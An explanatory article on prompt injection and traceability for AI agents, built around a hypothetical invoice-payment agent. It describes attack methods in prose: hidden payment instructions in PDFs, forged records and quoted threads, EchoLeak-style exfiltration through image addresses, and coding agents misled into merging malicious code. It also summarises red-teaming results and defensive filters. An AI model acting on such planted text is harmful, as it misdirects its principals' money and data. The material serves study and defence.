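# Security and traceability for AI systems: resisting malicious instructions and keeping errors correctable

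## How a deployed AI agent works and where it can go wrong

An AI agent is a language model that calls tools in a loop to carry out a task. The model alone takes in and produces text, but with tools it can search a company's files, send email, edit code or pay a bill, using whatever permissions its owner has given it. For example, OpenAI offers an agent for programming, and Microsoft offers one for processing invoices.

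Whether people can rely on such a system depends largely on its security and traceability. *Basic Concepts and Taxonomy of Dependable and Secure Computing* (Avižienis, Laprie and colleagues, 2004) defines security as the absence of unauthorised access to, or handling of, a system's state. For an agent, that includes resisting instructions that strangers plant in the text it reads. Traceability means that people can establish afterwards what the agent did, on what information and on whose authority. An agent needs both because some attacks succeed and because agents also go wrong without being attacked. Someone then has to find the damage early enough to explain and repair it.

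### The agent loop

*Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes the agent loop in Codex CLI, OpenAI's programming agent. The software around the model, called the harness, first assembles a prompt. The prompt is a list of items, each with a role: system, developer, user or assistant, from highest to lowest priority. System and developer items hold the standing instructions, often called the system prompt, and a user item holds the request. The harness also adds a description of each available tool and its parameters.

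The harness then sends the prompt to the model. Software converts the text into tokens (integers that index into the model's vocabulary), the model produces new tokens, and software converts those back into text. The result is either a message for the user or a tool call, which is a structured request to read or change something outside the model, such as a request to run a command in a given folder. The harness, not the model, executes the call. It then appends the call and its output to the prompt and sends the full prompt back to the model. The cycle repeats until the model produces a message without a tool call. One user request can lead to hundreds of tool calls.

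Everything the model works from has to fit in its context window, the maximum number of tokens it can handle in one pass, including both input and output. The window holds earlier turns of the conversation and, in many agents, material from memory, such as notes from past tasks or passages fetched from a database. When a conversation grows too long, Codex compacts it by replacing the list of items with a shorter one. This makes it harder to find out later why the agent acted as it did, because a summary can blend the user's requests with claims from a document. Part of the compacted list in Codex is also encrypted, so a person reading it on their own machine learns little from it.

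*The Landscape of Prompt Injection Threats in LLM Agents* (Wang, Li and colleagues, 2026), a survey of 78 papers on attacks and defences, describes much the same loop in six steps. It points out that an agent keeps all its inputs in one context memory, separated only by textual markers, whereas ordinary programs take in different kinds of input through separate interfaces. The survey treats the system prompt and the user's request as trusted, the results of tool calls as untrusted, and databases and training data as something in between, but the model processes them all as a single sequence. OpenAI trains its models to rank the sources, with system instructions first, then developer, user and tool. This training makes the models more likely to follow the ranking, but it does not isolate the sources from one another. That leaves room for prompt injection, an attack in which text from someone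 without authority leads the agent to act against the wishes of the people it works for.

Hard limits therefore have to be built into the surrounding software, and they may not cover every tool. Codex runs its own command tool in a sandbox, a restricted environment. Tools that the user adds from outside run without that sandbox and, as Bolin notes, have to enforce their own limits. The prompt also includes instructions on which folders the model may write to and when to ask for permission, but the sandbox is what blocks a forbidden write.

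### An invoice agent

Suppose a company's finance department uses an agent to pay suppliers. The agent has four tools: one reads a mailbox and opens attached PDF invoices, one searches company files (contracts, purchase orders, and the supplier list with bank details), one sends email from the company's address, and one creates payments at the bank.

On an ordinary day a paper supplier emails an invoice for €18,400, and a clerk types a request to pay whatever has come in. The run goes like this:

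1. The model produces a call to read the mailbox. The harness fetches the email, extracts the text of the PDF and appends both to the prompt.
2. The model produces a search for the supplier. The harness appends the matching record, with its account number.
3. The model produces a payment call containing a payee, an amount and an account number. The harness passes it to the bank and appends the confirmation.
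4. The model produces a message to the clerk: the invoice is paid.

Anthropic, the developer of the Claude models, uses the word "principals" for those whose instructions a model should give weight to and on whose behalf it should act. Claude has three: Anthropic, operators (the businesses that build products on the model) and users. OpenAI lists a matching set of sources of instructions for its own models: OpenAI, developers and users. The invoice agent's principals are the model's developer, the company (whose instructions are in the system prompt) and the clerk. The supplier is not a principal, although the company owes it money and its interests count for something. Anthropic also distinguishes between those whose instructions carry weight and those whose interests do.

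All other text is untrusted content. This includes the emails and PDFs. It also includes the file search results, since a folder of contracts will contain documents that outsiders wrote. If the company has one agent read invoices for another, the reading agent's output is untrusted too. Anthropic's rule is that the agent should treat instructions in untrusted content as information, not as commands.

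The rule is awkward to apply to invoices. "Please note our new bank account" is an instruction in form, but it is also a normal thing for a supplier to write, because firms do change banks. An agent that ignores every such line will pay into closed accounts, but if it acts on all of them, anyone who can send an email can redirect the company's money. The agent must treat the line as a claim, and someone must check it against a source the sender does not control.

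Finally, the agent has wide permissions. It can read outside mail and internal files, write in the company's name and spend its money. Microsoft sells a similar but more limited agent. According to Microsoft's *FAQ for Payables Agent*, it watches a mailbox for PDF invoices, matches each to a known vendor and drafts a purchase invoice, but posts nothing without a person's approval. It acts under its own user identity, within permissions that an administrator sets. When it creates a record for a new vendor, the record stays blocked until a person releases it. Microsoft's *Payables Agent overview (preview)* explains that the record is blocked because companies usually confirm a new vendor's bank account by calling the vendor's finance department.

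The invoice agent with a payment tool is a harder case than this product, but a plausible one. The same preview page marks some steps that are currently required as meant to become optional over time.

### Fault, error and failure

People say "the agent made an error" about almost anything that goes wrong, which obscures where someone could have intervened. Engineers who study dependable systems use stricter terms. Avižienis and colleagues define a failure as an event in which the service a system delivers departs from correct service, meaning what the system is intended to do. An error is the part of the system's state that may lead to a failure, and a fault is the "adjudged or hypothesized cause" of an error.

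An invoice might contain an instruction, in white type on a white background, for any AI system reading it to use a different bank account. The instruction is a fault, and because it comes from outside with malicious intent, it is also an attack. Once the attacker's account number is in the context window as the number to pay, the agent's state contains an error. The failure occurs when the bank moves the money. An outside fault can usually do harm only if the system already has a vulnerability, which is an internal fault that lets it in. One vulnerability here is that the harness accepts any account number the model writes into a payment call. That vulnerability may have been dormant for a year because every invoice was legitimate.

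Many errors never become failures. If the agent looks up the supplier list after reading the PDF and replaces the planted account number with the listed one, the error is gone before it causes any loss. A check can also stop an error before it causes a failure, whether a program compares account numbers or a person approves drafts. However, human approval is only reliable if the person reviews each draft carefully. *A2AS* (2025), a proposal for securing agents while they run, points out that employees cannot guarantee that they will verify invoice details at scale.

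Whether something is an error or a failure depends on what we include in the system. A payment call with the wrong account is a failure of the model, but in a system that also includes the harness and an approving clerk, it is an error that the system may still catch. A failure in one system is also a fault for the next. After the wrong payment, the company's accounts show the paper supplier as paid. That entry is a new error in a different system, and it can remain until the supplier asks for its money.

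In the taxonomy, correct service means fulfilling the system's purpose, which its written instructions may describe badly. Suppose the system prompt tells an agent to pay every invoice that matches a purchase order, and a supplier sends the same invoice twice. The agent follows its instructions exactly and pays twice, but the system has still failed. The fault is in the specification, and Avižienis and colleagues observe that people may recognise such failures only afterwards, from their consequences.

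Failures also differ in whether they trigger a warning. By default, a wrong payment does not. The bank accurately confirms that it made the payment it was instructed to make, and the agent's closing message repeats that the payment succeeded.

### Three sources of the same wrong payment

The hidden sentence is one way €18,400 can end up in the wrong account. An authorised user can also cause this, and so can the agent on its own.

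| Where the harm starts | Fault | Error | Failure |
|---|---|---|---|
| A stranger | A hidden sentence in the PDF names another bank account | The attacker's account number stands in the payment call | €18,400 reaches an account that is not the supplier's |
| An authorised user | The clerk tells the agent to pay an account the clerk controls | The clerk's account number stands in the payment call | €18,400 reaches an account that is not the supplier's |
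| The agent itself | The model matches the invoice to another firm with a similar name | The other firm's account number stands in the payment call | €18,400 reaches an account that is not the supplier's |

*A2AS* describes an attack by a stranger as a scenario, without an experiment behind it. Zscaler, a security company, found a similar attack on the open web. A site offering software for programmers contained text, positioned off screen where human visitors couldn't see it, that gave AI agents step-by-step instructions to pay a small licence fee in cryptocurrency. Zscaler built an agent with a browser and a payment tool and tested it on the site in a sandbox with 26 language models. The agent paid with four of them, two Llama models and two Gemini models, according to SC Media's *Malicious websites trick AI agents into crypto payments, context poisoning*. The result shows that the attack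 can work against some models in current use. The test used only one trap, so it does not measure how often a patient attacker would succeed. The site's wallet had received no payment of the amount the page asked for, so it is unclear whether any real agent ever paid.

Defences that distinguish an agent's principals from strangers do not stop a dishonest clerk who has full authority to instruct it. OpenAI's *Model Spec* (2025), the company's account of how its models should behave, lists harmful instructions from users or developers as a risk separate from the assistant's own errors. Two decades earlier, Avižienis and colleagues noted that some authorised people have malicious objectives, and counted corrupt insiders among a system's intruders. Most of the remedies are old bookkeeping controls, such as requiring a second person to approve a change of bank details.

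An agent can make mistakes even when no one is attacking it. Microsoft warns that its product can match vendors incorrectly. When the product can't find an exact match on registration numbers, it looks for similar names and addresses instead. A model may also misread a digit in a poor scan.

Real cases can fit more than one of these categories. For example, a fraudster might phone the clerk, pose as the supplier and give a new account number, which the clerk passes to the agent in good faith. The agent has received a valid instruction from a principal, but the harm began with a stranger. Payables fraud often starts with one fake supplier request, according to PYMNTS Intelligence's *Accounts Payable Fraud in the Age of AI*. Classifying such a case correctly requires knowing about the phone call, which no log of the agent's tool calls will contain.

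The bank can't tell where a payment instruction came from, because it receives only a plausible amount and account number. Measures against one source may not stop the other two, so a company that has dealt with hidden text still needs a way to detect a misdirected payment and recover the money. It also needs to know the cause in order to decide whether to block a sender, dismiss a clerk or change the matching rule. Running the agent again on the same invoice may not reveal the cause, because a model samples its output and may not repeat the mistake. Avižienis and colleagues use the term "elusive" for faults that people cannot reliably reproduce. To investigate one, the company has to rely on whatever records exist from the original run.

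Anyone who gives an agent such permissions has to consider whether someone can mislead it, whether anyone would notice, whether an investigator could reconstruct the cause, and whether anyone could undo the effect. The last two depend heavily on how quickly someone notices the problem. Microsoft, for instance, stores the prompts and responses of its Payables Agent for 20 days, for use in support requests. If a payment goes to the wrong account, a supplier who chases unpaid bills once a month may not complain until day 30. By then the stored prompts and responses are gone, and the money has probably been moved out of that account.

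## Prompt injection: what it is and why it is hard to rule out

The hidden sentence in the supplier's PDF is a prompt injection because its author has no authority over the agent and uses the sentence to make the agent act against its principals' wishes. A line naming a new bank account is an injection if a fraudster planted it and the agent pays the fraudster. If the clerk types the same line into the request, it is an instruction, even if it is an unwise one.

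Wang and colleagues sort these attacks by how the malicious text reaches the agent. In direct injection, the attacker types it into the conversation. In indirect injection, the attacker leaves it in an email, web page or file that the agent will read. In supply-chain injection, the attacker plants it in the database from which the agent retrieves passages, or in the model's training data.

Direct injection fits the definition less neatly, since the person typing is usually a user and therefore a principal. It still counts when a user tries to override someone who ranks higher. For example, a user might try to persuade a shop's chatbot to ignore the shop's pricing rules, which users have no authority to change. For the invoice agent, indirect injection matters most, because any stranger can send it email while only the clerk can type into its chat window.

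### Jailbreaks, misuse, poisoned memory and misinformation

In a jailbreak, a user gets a model to produce something its developer trained it to refuse, such as instructions for making a weapon. That request is harmful whoever makes it, but an injected request can be harmless in itself. For example, paying €18,400 to a supplier is a routine task for the invoice agent. Zverev, Abdelnabi and colleagues (2024) therefore argue in *Can LLMs Separate Instructions From Data?* that training a model to reject harmful prompts does not address injection, where the problem is the source of an instruction rather than its content.

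Misuse by an authorised user is not injection either. A clerk who tells the agent to pay the clerk's own account is abusing real authority.

Memory poisoning makes an injection last. Suppose the agent keeps notes between tasks. In March it reads a forged email and saves a note that the paper supplier has changed banks, and in April it pays the next invoice to the account in the note. Deleting the email before April would not help, because the false account number is already in the agent's own records, where it looks more trustworthy than it did in the email.

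Ordinary misinformation is the hardest of these to distinguish from injection. Suppose a supplier delivers 30 boxes of paper and bills for 40. The agent correctly reads the bill as the supplier's claim, but wrongly believes it. The company has been exposed to that trick for as long as it has had suppliers. In an injection, the agent is wrong about whose words it is reading, and treats a stranger's text as if it came from a principal or from a source the principals rely on.

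### Older versions of the problem

The programmer Simon Willison named prompt injection in 2022 and compared it to SQL injection, an attack on databases (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026, *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents*). At that point the attacker was usually someone typing into a chatbot. In 2023 Kai Greshake and colleagues showed that the attacker need not take part in the conversation. According to *Trustworthy Agentic AI* (2026), a review of how agents fail, they demonstrated this kind of attack, called indirect injection, against several applications already in use.

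Computer scientists had known the underlying problem for much longer. In 1988 Norm Hardy described a compiler on a shared computer that had permission to write to a system directory so it could keep usage statistics there. Users could not write to the billing file in the same directory, but they could tell the compiler where to put its debugging output. When one of them named the billing file, the compiler overwrote it. Hardy called the compiler a confused deputy because it held permissions from the computer's owner, took requests from users, and could not tell whose authority it was using when it wrote a file. The invoice agent is in the same position, because it reads what a supplier sends and can make payments from the company's account, which the supplier cannot.

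SQL injection is the closer comparison, because programmers found a dependable fix for it. Suppose the company has a web form for looking up suppliers. A program pastes the name someone types into a command in SQL, the language programs use to communicate with databases, and sends the result to the database. An attacker types a name that contains a quotation mark followed by their own command. The database's parser, which works out the command's structure, treats the quotation mark as the end of the name and the rest as a command to execute.

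With a parameterised query, the program first sends the command with an empty slot where the name belongs. The database parses the command and fixes its structure before the program supplies the name, so the database can treat the name only as a value. Nobody has to recognise a malicious name, and a person called O'Brien can still use the form. Narisetty and colleagues conclude that separating commands from data structurally, rather than improving detection, also stopped other attacks of this family, including those that inject scripts into web pages.

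A prompt has no slot that the model is guaranteed to treat only as data. A developer can mark an email as data, but the model learned to respond to such markers in training and doesn't always follow them. SQL's grammar determines where a value ends, whereas in English an order and a report of an order can use the same words. The agent also has to understand the instructions in the email to do its job. A payables agent needs information such as "Please pay within 14 days", and the model interprets that sentence by the same process it applies to the clerk's request.

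### Measuring the missing boundary

Zverev and colleagues turned this complaint into a quantity. They treat a model as a function *g* with two inputs, one for instructions (*s*) and one for data (*d*). They then take a further piece of text, a probe *x*, which reads like a small task, and compare what the model does when the probe is in the data with what it does when the probe is in the instructions:

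$$\mathrm{sep}(g) = \mathbb{E}\left[\,\mathcal{D}\big(g(s,\,x+d),\; g(s+x,\,d)\big)\right]$$

Here $\mathcal{D}$ measures how much the two output distributions differ, and $\mathbb{E}$ is the average over many triples of instruction, data and probe. The score is zero for a model that joins its inputs together, because its output is the same in both cases, and high for a model that never follows instructions in its data input.

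Nobody can compute this exactly for a real model, so the researchers built a test with 9,160 items. In one, the model is told to judge whether a text about a product launch is positive or negative, and the text ends with a request to name a group of crows. If the word "murder" appears in the answer, the model has followed the request. The practical score covers only items where the expected word appears when the request is among the instructions. It is the share of those items where the word does not appear when the request is in the data.

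The nine models tested scored between 13.3% (Phi-3-mini) and 73.2% (Gemma-2B). GPT-4 scored 20.8%, so it answered the stray question in about four out of five cases. More capable models in the same family tended to score lower, possibly because they could do both tasks at once. Prompts that explained the distinction raised GPT-4's score to 95.3%, although GPT-4 had also helped to write the test items. Further training raised the average score of the seven open models from 37.5% to 95.5%. However, these models also carried out fewer of the probes that were proper instructions (50.0%, down from 67.8%), so some of the gain came from their becoming worse at following instructions altogether.

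These figures are out of date, since the models are from 2023 and 2024. The test was also somewhat harsh on them, because it put the data in the user's turn and developers train models to answer users. Training has since removed much of the behaviour, at least for familiar attacks. When Choi, Kim and colleagues (2026), in *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents*, tried 935 existing injected instructions on an agent built on GPT-5.2, 0.2% succeeded, although the model still received instructions and data as one sequence.

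*ASIDE* (2025) proposes a way to help language models distinguish instructions from data. A model turns each token into a vector before processing it, and the proposal is to rotate the vectors of all data tokens, so that the same word has a different vector depending on whether it belongs to an instruction or to data. Models with this change separated the two better even without safety training. The rotation makes the distinction easier to learn but doesn't enforce it, as a parser would. Someone must also decide beforehand which text is data, and with an agent that is often the difficult part.

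### Two emails to the invoice agent

The earlier email that reads "please use our new bank account" is not an attack if the supplier really has changed banks, and in that case the company wants the agent to pay the new account. If a fraudster wrote the email and the agent pays because of it, that is prompt injection. The fraudster was free to tell the company something but had no authority to decide where its money goes, and used the email to do so anyway. The two emails can be identical, so no one can tell them apart by inspecting the text alone.

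Suppose instead that the clerk calls the supplier on the number in the company's files, and a fraudster who has taken over the phone line confirms the change. The company has then fallen for ordinary fraud, since the email led only to a phone call, as it should have.

Researchers differ on what counts as prompt injection. *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections* (Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian, 2026) includes an email that asks for a travel refund and falsely states that the department head has approved it. Choi and colleagues distinguish their own attack from hidden text in a résumé that invents work experience, because the model screening the résumé still reads the text as coming from the applicant. One reasonable distinction between the two examples is that the invented approval takes the place of a decision that belonged to the department head, while the invented work experience only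 makes the applicant look better.

Now suppose the clerk writes, "Anna in purchasing has emailed a list of changes to the supplier file, please make them." An email is normally untrusted content, but the clerk has given Anna's instructions some authority, and an agent that ignores them fails at its task. Wang and colleagues call such tasks context-dependent and found that existing benchmarks largely leave them out. Those benchmarks therefore favour defences that disregard any instructions in the content the agent reads, because they seldom test the tasks on which such defences fail.

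It is hard to say how much authority the clerk has given Anna's list. If the list ends with a request to send the supplier's contract to an outside address, the clerk probably did not mean to allow that. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian tested how well models judge these limits in 300 constructed conversations. In each, a user let a sender request a certain kind of action, and the sender later asked for something outside that scope. When that request came straight after the delegation, Claude Sonnet 4.6 carried it out in 29.9% of cases and GPT-5.4 in 36.2%. When one to ten proper requests came first, the rates fell to 7.0% and 24.5%, so seeing normal requests helped Claude Sonnet 4.6 considerably more than GPT-5.4.

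In a second test, a colleague's email asked for a permitted internal task and an unapproved message to an outsider. GPT-5.2 sent the message in 65 of 100 scenarios, GPT-5.4 in 34 and Claude Sonnet 4.6 in 6. When the user had said that external messages required sign-off, GPT-5.2 sent 12 and the other two models sent none. Neither test involved an attacker, but one who could get a sentence into Anna's list could exploit the same weakness.

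### False data with no instruction in it

Choi and colleagues showed in July 2026 that an attack can work without hiding instructions in data, which is how people often describe prompt injection. They call this attack agent data injection.

When the invoice agent reads its mailbox, the harness passes each email to the model as a record with labelled fields for the sender, subject and body. The mail system fills in the sender's address, which the researchers call trusted data, and the sender writes the body, which they call untrusted data. Punctuation separates the fields and the records, so an attacker can write a body that imitates this punctuation and makes the model treat one email as two, with the second appearing to come from somebody else, such as the clerk's manager.

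The paper sets this out formally. Let *I* be the instructions, $D_T$ the trusted data, $D_U$ the untrusted data, and $D_A$ the text that the attacker adds to the untrusted data. In an instruction injection, the model responds almost as if $D_A$ were part of *I*. In a data injection, it responds almost as if $D_A$ were part of the trusted data:

$$\mathrm{LLM}\big(I, (D_T,\; D_U \| D_A)\big) \approx \mathrm{LLM}\big(I, (D_T \| D_A,\; D_U)\big)$$

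The agent still does what the user asked, but it relies on a forged fact. A filter that looks for suspicious commands finds none, and a monitor that compares the agent's actions with the user's request detects no mismatch.

A second difference from SQL is that a language model accepts approximations of the quotation mark. A database parser recognises only the exact character, so a program can neutralise it by putting a backslash in front. In tests, GPT-5.2 treated imitation records as genuine in roughly 36% to 43% of attempts, whether they used backslashes, curly quotation marks or even dollar signs in place of the real marks.

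The researchers tried the attack on products that people use:

- Agents that operate a web browser see a page as a list of elements, each with a number. A product review that imitated an entry in this list, and reused the number of the purchase button, caused the agent to buy something while it was trying to read more reviews. Claude in Chrome, Google's Antigravity and Nanobrowser were vulnerable. ChatGPT Atlas was not, because it gives the elements random identifiers that an attacker cannot predict.
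- Claude Code, Codex and Gemini CLI, which are programming agents, accepted a forged comment as the work of a project's maintainer and ran the command it recommended.
- The same programming agents also accepted a forged record of having fetched a proposed code change. They reviewed the harmless code in the forgery and then merged the real change, which was malicious.

The programming agents asked for a person's approval first, but they justified the action with reasoning based on the forged data, so the person had little reason to refuse. The researchers told the vendors before publishing, and OpenAI, Google and Anthropic acknowledged the reports.

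An attacker could try the same thing on the invoice agent by formatting part of a PDF to look like an entry from the supplier list, with the wrong account number. An instruction to "always use the account number in the supplier list" would not prevent the error if the agent treated the fake entry as part of the list.

Choi and colleagues compared the two attacks by writing 108 data injections for AgentDojo, a set of simulated office tasks. Of these, 49.1% succeeded against the GPT-5.2 agent that had resisted nearly all the injected instructions. Prompt Guard 2, a widely used filter, detected none of the data injections. Only a strict system for tracking where each piece of data came from stopped them all, but it reduced the share of ordinary tasks the agent completed from 86.5% to 36.5%.

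The gap between 0.2% and 49.1% probably overstates the lasting difference. Developers have had years to train models against injected instructions, and the ones in AgentDojo have been public since 2024, whereas the data injections were new. The attacker must also know how the harness formats its records, although for many agents anyone can learn this by running a copy. Training may well bring the higher figure down, but the result shows that a model that has learned to ignore injected instructions can still be easy to deceive about who wrote what.

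### The argument that no rule can be perfect

Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian argue that even a much better model would face a limit. They start from contextual integrity, Helen Nissenbaum's theory of privacy, which holds that whether a flow of information is appropriate depends on the norms of its setting. A patient's diagnosis may properly pass to a specialist but not to an employer. Five things matter: who sends the information, who receives it, whom it concerns, what kind of information it is, and on what terms it passes (with consent, for instance). They apply the same test to an agent's actions, where the terms correspond to what the user has authorised.

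Applied to the invoice agent, the argument has four steps:

1. Whether the agent should pay a new account depends on the context, such as whether the supplier really sent the email and whether the clerk has allowed such changes. The words of the email do not settle it.
2. The agent has no direct access to these facts. It works from evidence, some of which it or the harness can verify, and some of which it cannot.
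3. An attacker can make the unverified part look just as it would in a legitimate case, without contradicting anything that has passed a check.
4. There can therefore be two situations, one legitimate and one an attack, in which the agent has exactly the same evidence. Any rule it follows will make it pay with the same probability, *p*, in both.

The agent makes the wrong payment with probability *p* in the attack and blocks a proper payment with probability 1 − *p* in the legitimate case. These two error rates add up to 1, so at least one is a half or more. An agent that always decides the same way on the same evidence gets one of the two situations wrong every time.

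Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian argue that correct facts may not be enough either, because an attacker can also manipulate the agent's judgement of what serves the user. For example, an email may warn that an important client has been waiting since Monday and might leave. A quick reply is right if the warning is true, but the same warning is an attack if it is false.

The algebra is simple and correct. The conclusion depends on whether such pairs of situations exist, which the paper acknowledges its theorem does not establish. Whether they exist depends on what the agent can check and what the attacker controls. If the company calls every supplier who reports a new account, the honest supplier confirms the change and the victim of a forgery denies it, so the two situations no longer look alike. The attacker then needs a new pair, perhaps by taking over the phone line as well. The paper predicts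 that there will always be one, because an attacker can invent endless contexts while each check covers only some of them. That is plausible for an agent that handles all of someone's correspondence, but much less plausible for one that pays known suppliers from a fixed list.

The theorem applies equally to a clerk with the same email and the same means of checking it, so it cannot explain why an agent might do worse than a clerk. It also leaves out how often the two situations occur and how much harm each error does. Holding every change of account until someone has phoned will delay some honest suppliers by a few days, while accepting the changes will sometimes lose the company €18,400. Most finance departments would readily choose the delays, even though both rules produce errors.

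The experiments in the same paper are better evidence about current models than about the limit. One experiment used pairs of business emails that differed in a single clause. One version claimed that the recipient's assistant already had permission to act, and the other did not. Two versions of Prompt Guard could hardly distinguish them, scoring 0.43 and 0.59 on a scale where 0.5 is chance. A filter trained on such claims might do better, because the two clauses differ in wording, but no filter could determine from the email alone whether the claim is true.

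In another experiment, Claude Sonnet 4.6 wrote attack emails to an email assistant based on the same model and revised them after each failure. The user had asked only for a task such as a summary, so an attack succeeded if the assistant sent an email. With up to 45 attempts per scenario, the attacker succeeded in 96.7% of 150 scenarios, compared with 0.67% for the unrevised emails. It usually forged an earlier message from the user in a quoted thread, and the assistant mistook this for the user's own words.

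In a sense, this mistake was avoidable. The harness could identify which text the user had typed, and a rule that only typed text can grant permission would have defeated the forged quotations. It would also have made the assistant ignore every real approval that someone forwarded by email. The paper describes this trade-off, but the models in the test had not yet reached the point of having to make it.

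### What people have found in the wild

Malicious text found on a live page is the weakest evidence of real attacks. A demonstration that an attack works against a product is stronger, and confirmation that a victim lost something is the strongest. Most reports so far provide only the weakest kind.

Google searched Common Crawl, a public archive that stores 2 to 3 billion web pages a month, according to Help Net Security's *Indirect prompt injection is taking hold in the wild*. Its researchers looked for known injection patterns, then used Google's Gemini model and human reviewers to remove false alarms, SecurityWeek reports. Google found a great many false alarms because much of the apparent attack text was in research papers, blog posts and security articles about prompt injection.

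The real attempts were mostly crude. Google attributes most of them to individual site owners who seemed to be experimenting or playing pranks, according to passages quoted in Slashdot's *Google Studies Prompt Injection Attacks Against AI Agents Browsing the Web*. Some pages carried commands to delete every file on the reader's machine, which Google thought unlikely to work. The malicious category grew by 32% between November 2025 and February 2026, though that percentage alone does not show how many pages were involved. The search covered known patterns, so it would miss new ones, and it left out social media.

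In *10 Indirect Prompt Injection Payloads Caught in the Wild*, Sewani reports that researchers at the security company Forcepoint found text with more serious aims on live websites. The aims included financial fraud, destroying data and stealing the keys that programs use to log in to services. One page contained the full details of a PayPal transaction, meant for an agent with stored payment credentials. Forcepoint describes all ten texts as working attacks, but it is not counting victims. Whether such a text does any harm depends on what the AI system reading it can do. Sewani told Infosecurity Magazine, for *Researchers Uncover 10 In-the-Wild Prompt Injection Payloads Targeting AI Agents*, that a browser assistant that can only summarise is at low risk.

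Unit 42, the research group of the security company Palo Alto Networks, published *Fooling AI Agents* in March 2026. According to VPN Central's *Indirect prompt injection attacks are no longer theoretical*, Unit 42 documented 22 techniques for building such texts, and what it believes is the first observed attempt to use one to get an advertisement past an AI reviewer. The reviewer is a sensible target for an attacker because it has to read the page and its decision is worth money.

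Researchers who find malicious instructions on a web page cannot tell from the page whether any agent followed them. Evidence of a payment or a deleted file would be in the agent owner's systems, and the owner may not connect it with a page the agent visited. The licence-fee site that Zscaler found was easier to check because its payment address was public.

EchoLeak (CVE-2025-32711) is the best-known demonstration of prompt injection against a widely used product. It was a vulnerability in Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that answers employees' questions from their company's emails and documents. The security company Aim Security disclosed it in June 2025. An attacker sent an employee an email that looked ordinary. When the employee later asked Copilot a related question, Copilot fetched the email along with internal documents, and the text in the email led it to put confidential information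 into the address of an image. The employee's browser then automatically requested the image, sending the information to the attacker's server. The employee did not have to click on anything or even open the email.

Microsoft fixed the fault on its own servers and said that no customers had been affected. The whole EchoLeak chain worked against a real product, but it has no known victims. Theft could have gone unnoticed, though, because the stolen information would have left the company in a request that looked like a browser loading a picture.

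## Training and filtering models to resist malicious instructions

A company that uses an AI agent to process invoices cannot prevent strangers from emailing the agent, so developers try to limit what an email can make it do. They can train the model to give less weight to instructions in the content it reads, screen that content before the model sees it, or check the model's tool calls before the harness executes them. Each method stops many attacks, but published success rates for attacks on defended models still range from zero to 100%, and much of that variation comes from how hard the testers tried.

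### Training a ranking of sources

OpenAI uses examples to train its models to follow a ranking of instruction sources, called the instruction hierarchy. In examples where the sources agree, OpenAI splits a request, such as one for a 20-line poem in Spanish, between the system prompt and the user's message, and trains the model to satisfy every part. In examples where the sources conflict, it trains the model to answer as if the lower-ranking instruction were absent. A supplier's email reaches the invoice agent as a tool result, which ranks lowest, so any instruction in the email that contradicts the clerk should have no effect.

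OpenAI trained GPT-5 Mini further on conflicting instructions. Its score rose from 0.84 to 0.95 in tests where the user contradicted the system prompt and from 0.83 to 0.95 where the user contradicted the developer, but stayed at 0.86 where the developer contradicted the system prompt. Its results in science and mathematics hardly changed. Its win rate in conversation against an older model, o1, fell from 0.71 to 0.66, so the training seems to have made its ordinary answers slightly less appealing.

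A ranking of instructions does not help with forged records like the ones Choi and colleagues used, because those contain no instruction to rank.

A company that builds on someone else's model usually can't retrain it, but it can change the prompt. One method, Spotlighting, adds markers to the prompt so that the model can distinguish untrusted text from the rest. Another, Prompt Sandwiching, repeats the user's request after the untrusted text so that the request comes last in the prompt. Both methods are easy to add, but they depend on the model responding to the markers or the repeated request as intended.

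### Training on attacks

Developers also train models on the attacks themselves. For Claude Opus 4.5, Anthropic put prompt injections into simulated web pages and rewarded the model for recognising them and refusing to comply, even when they sounded official or urgent. The quality of this training depends on how varied the attacks are. *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection* (Zorz, 2026) describes research in which training on more attacks left agents easier to hijack, because large collections often repeat the same attack.

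Developers can train a model to find new attacks. OpenAI's GPT-Red sends a prompt, observes the response and tries again until it reaches a goal such as stealing data. Help Net Security's *GPT-Red beat human red teamers on a prompt injection test* (2026) reports that GPT-Red and several defending models learn at the same time. GPT-Red earns a reward when it causes a valid failure, and the defenders earn one when they resist and still finish their original task. Without the second condition, a model could score perfectly by refusing every task. As the defenders improve, GPT-Red has to find different attacks. OpenAI says this training used about as much computing power as some of its largest post-training runs.

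GPT-Red succeeded against GPT-5.1, an older model, in 84% of scenarios it had not trained on, while human testers succeeded in only a small share of them. It also attacked an AI agent that ran a real vending machine in OpenAI's office. After practising in a simulation, it got the agent to cut the price of one item to $0.50, offer an expensive new item at the same price and cancel another customer's order.

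OpenAI has used these attacks to train each of its releases since GPT-5.3. GPT-5.6 Sol, from the summer of 2026, failed on 0.05% of GPT-Red's direct injections, with no loss of general ability and no increase in needless refusals. However, the model had trained against GPT-Red, so this result is mainly evidence about attacks like GPT-Red's.

### Filters on incoming text and outgoing actions

A filter on incoming text is usually a small language model trained on examples to distinguish known attacks from ordinary text. It gives each document a score, and if the score exceeds a threshold, the harness withholds the document or warns the main model. According to Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5, the company runs such filters, which it calls probes, on tool results in many of its products.

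A filter's threshold is hard to set for an agent that processes invoices, because ordinary invoices also contain commands. A strict filter will hold up real bills, while a lenient one will let through an attack that reads like a bill.

A classifier on outgoing actions examines the tool call instead. It may flag a payment to an unfamiliar account as suspicious without finding the hidden sentence in the PDF that led to it. In a setting called auto mode, Anthropic uses probes to inspect incoming text and a second classifier to block potentially dangerous tool calls, so an attack has to get past both.

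Anthropic describes the two layers as failing independently. If each missed 5% of attacks, independent layers would together miss only 0.25%. The real figure would be higher if the same attacks tended to get past both. For instance, an email giving a convincing business reason for paying into a new account may pass the first filter because nothing in it looks like an attack, and the second because the payment seems justified.

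### Harmful requests from authorised users

When an authorised user asks an agent to write malware, the model has to judge the request by its content, because ranking instructions by their source doesn't help. It also has to avoid refusing the many legitimate requests that look similar, since security staff scan networks and test websites for weaknesses as part of their work.

Anthropic tests its models with 61 malicious requests and 61 sensitive but permitted ones, running each ten times in Claude Code, its programming agent. Claude Opus 5 refused 89.00% of the malicious runs and carried out 99.82% of the permitted ones. Claude Sonnet 5 refused more of the malicious runs (92.37%) but carried out only 91.55% of the permitted ones. In a second test, with 112 harmful tasks for an agent that operates a computer, Opus 5 refused 93.75%, up from 81.70% for its predecessor, Opus 4.8. Anthropic ran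 both tests without the extra safeguards a product may add.

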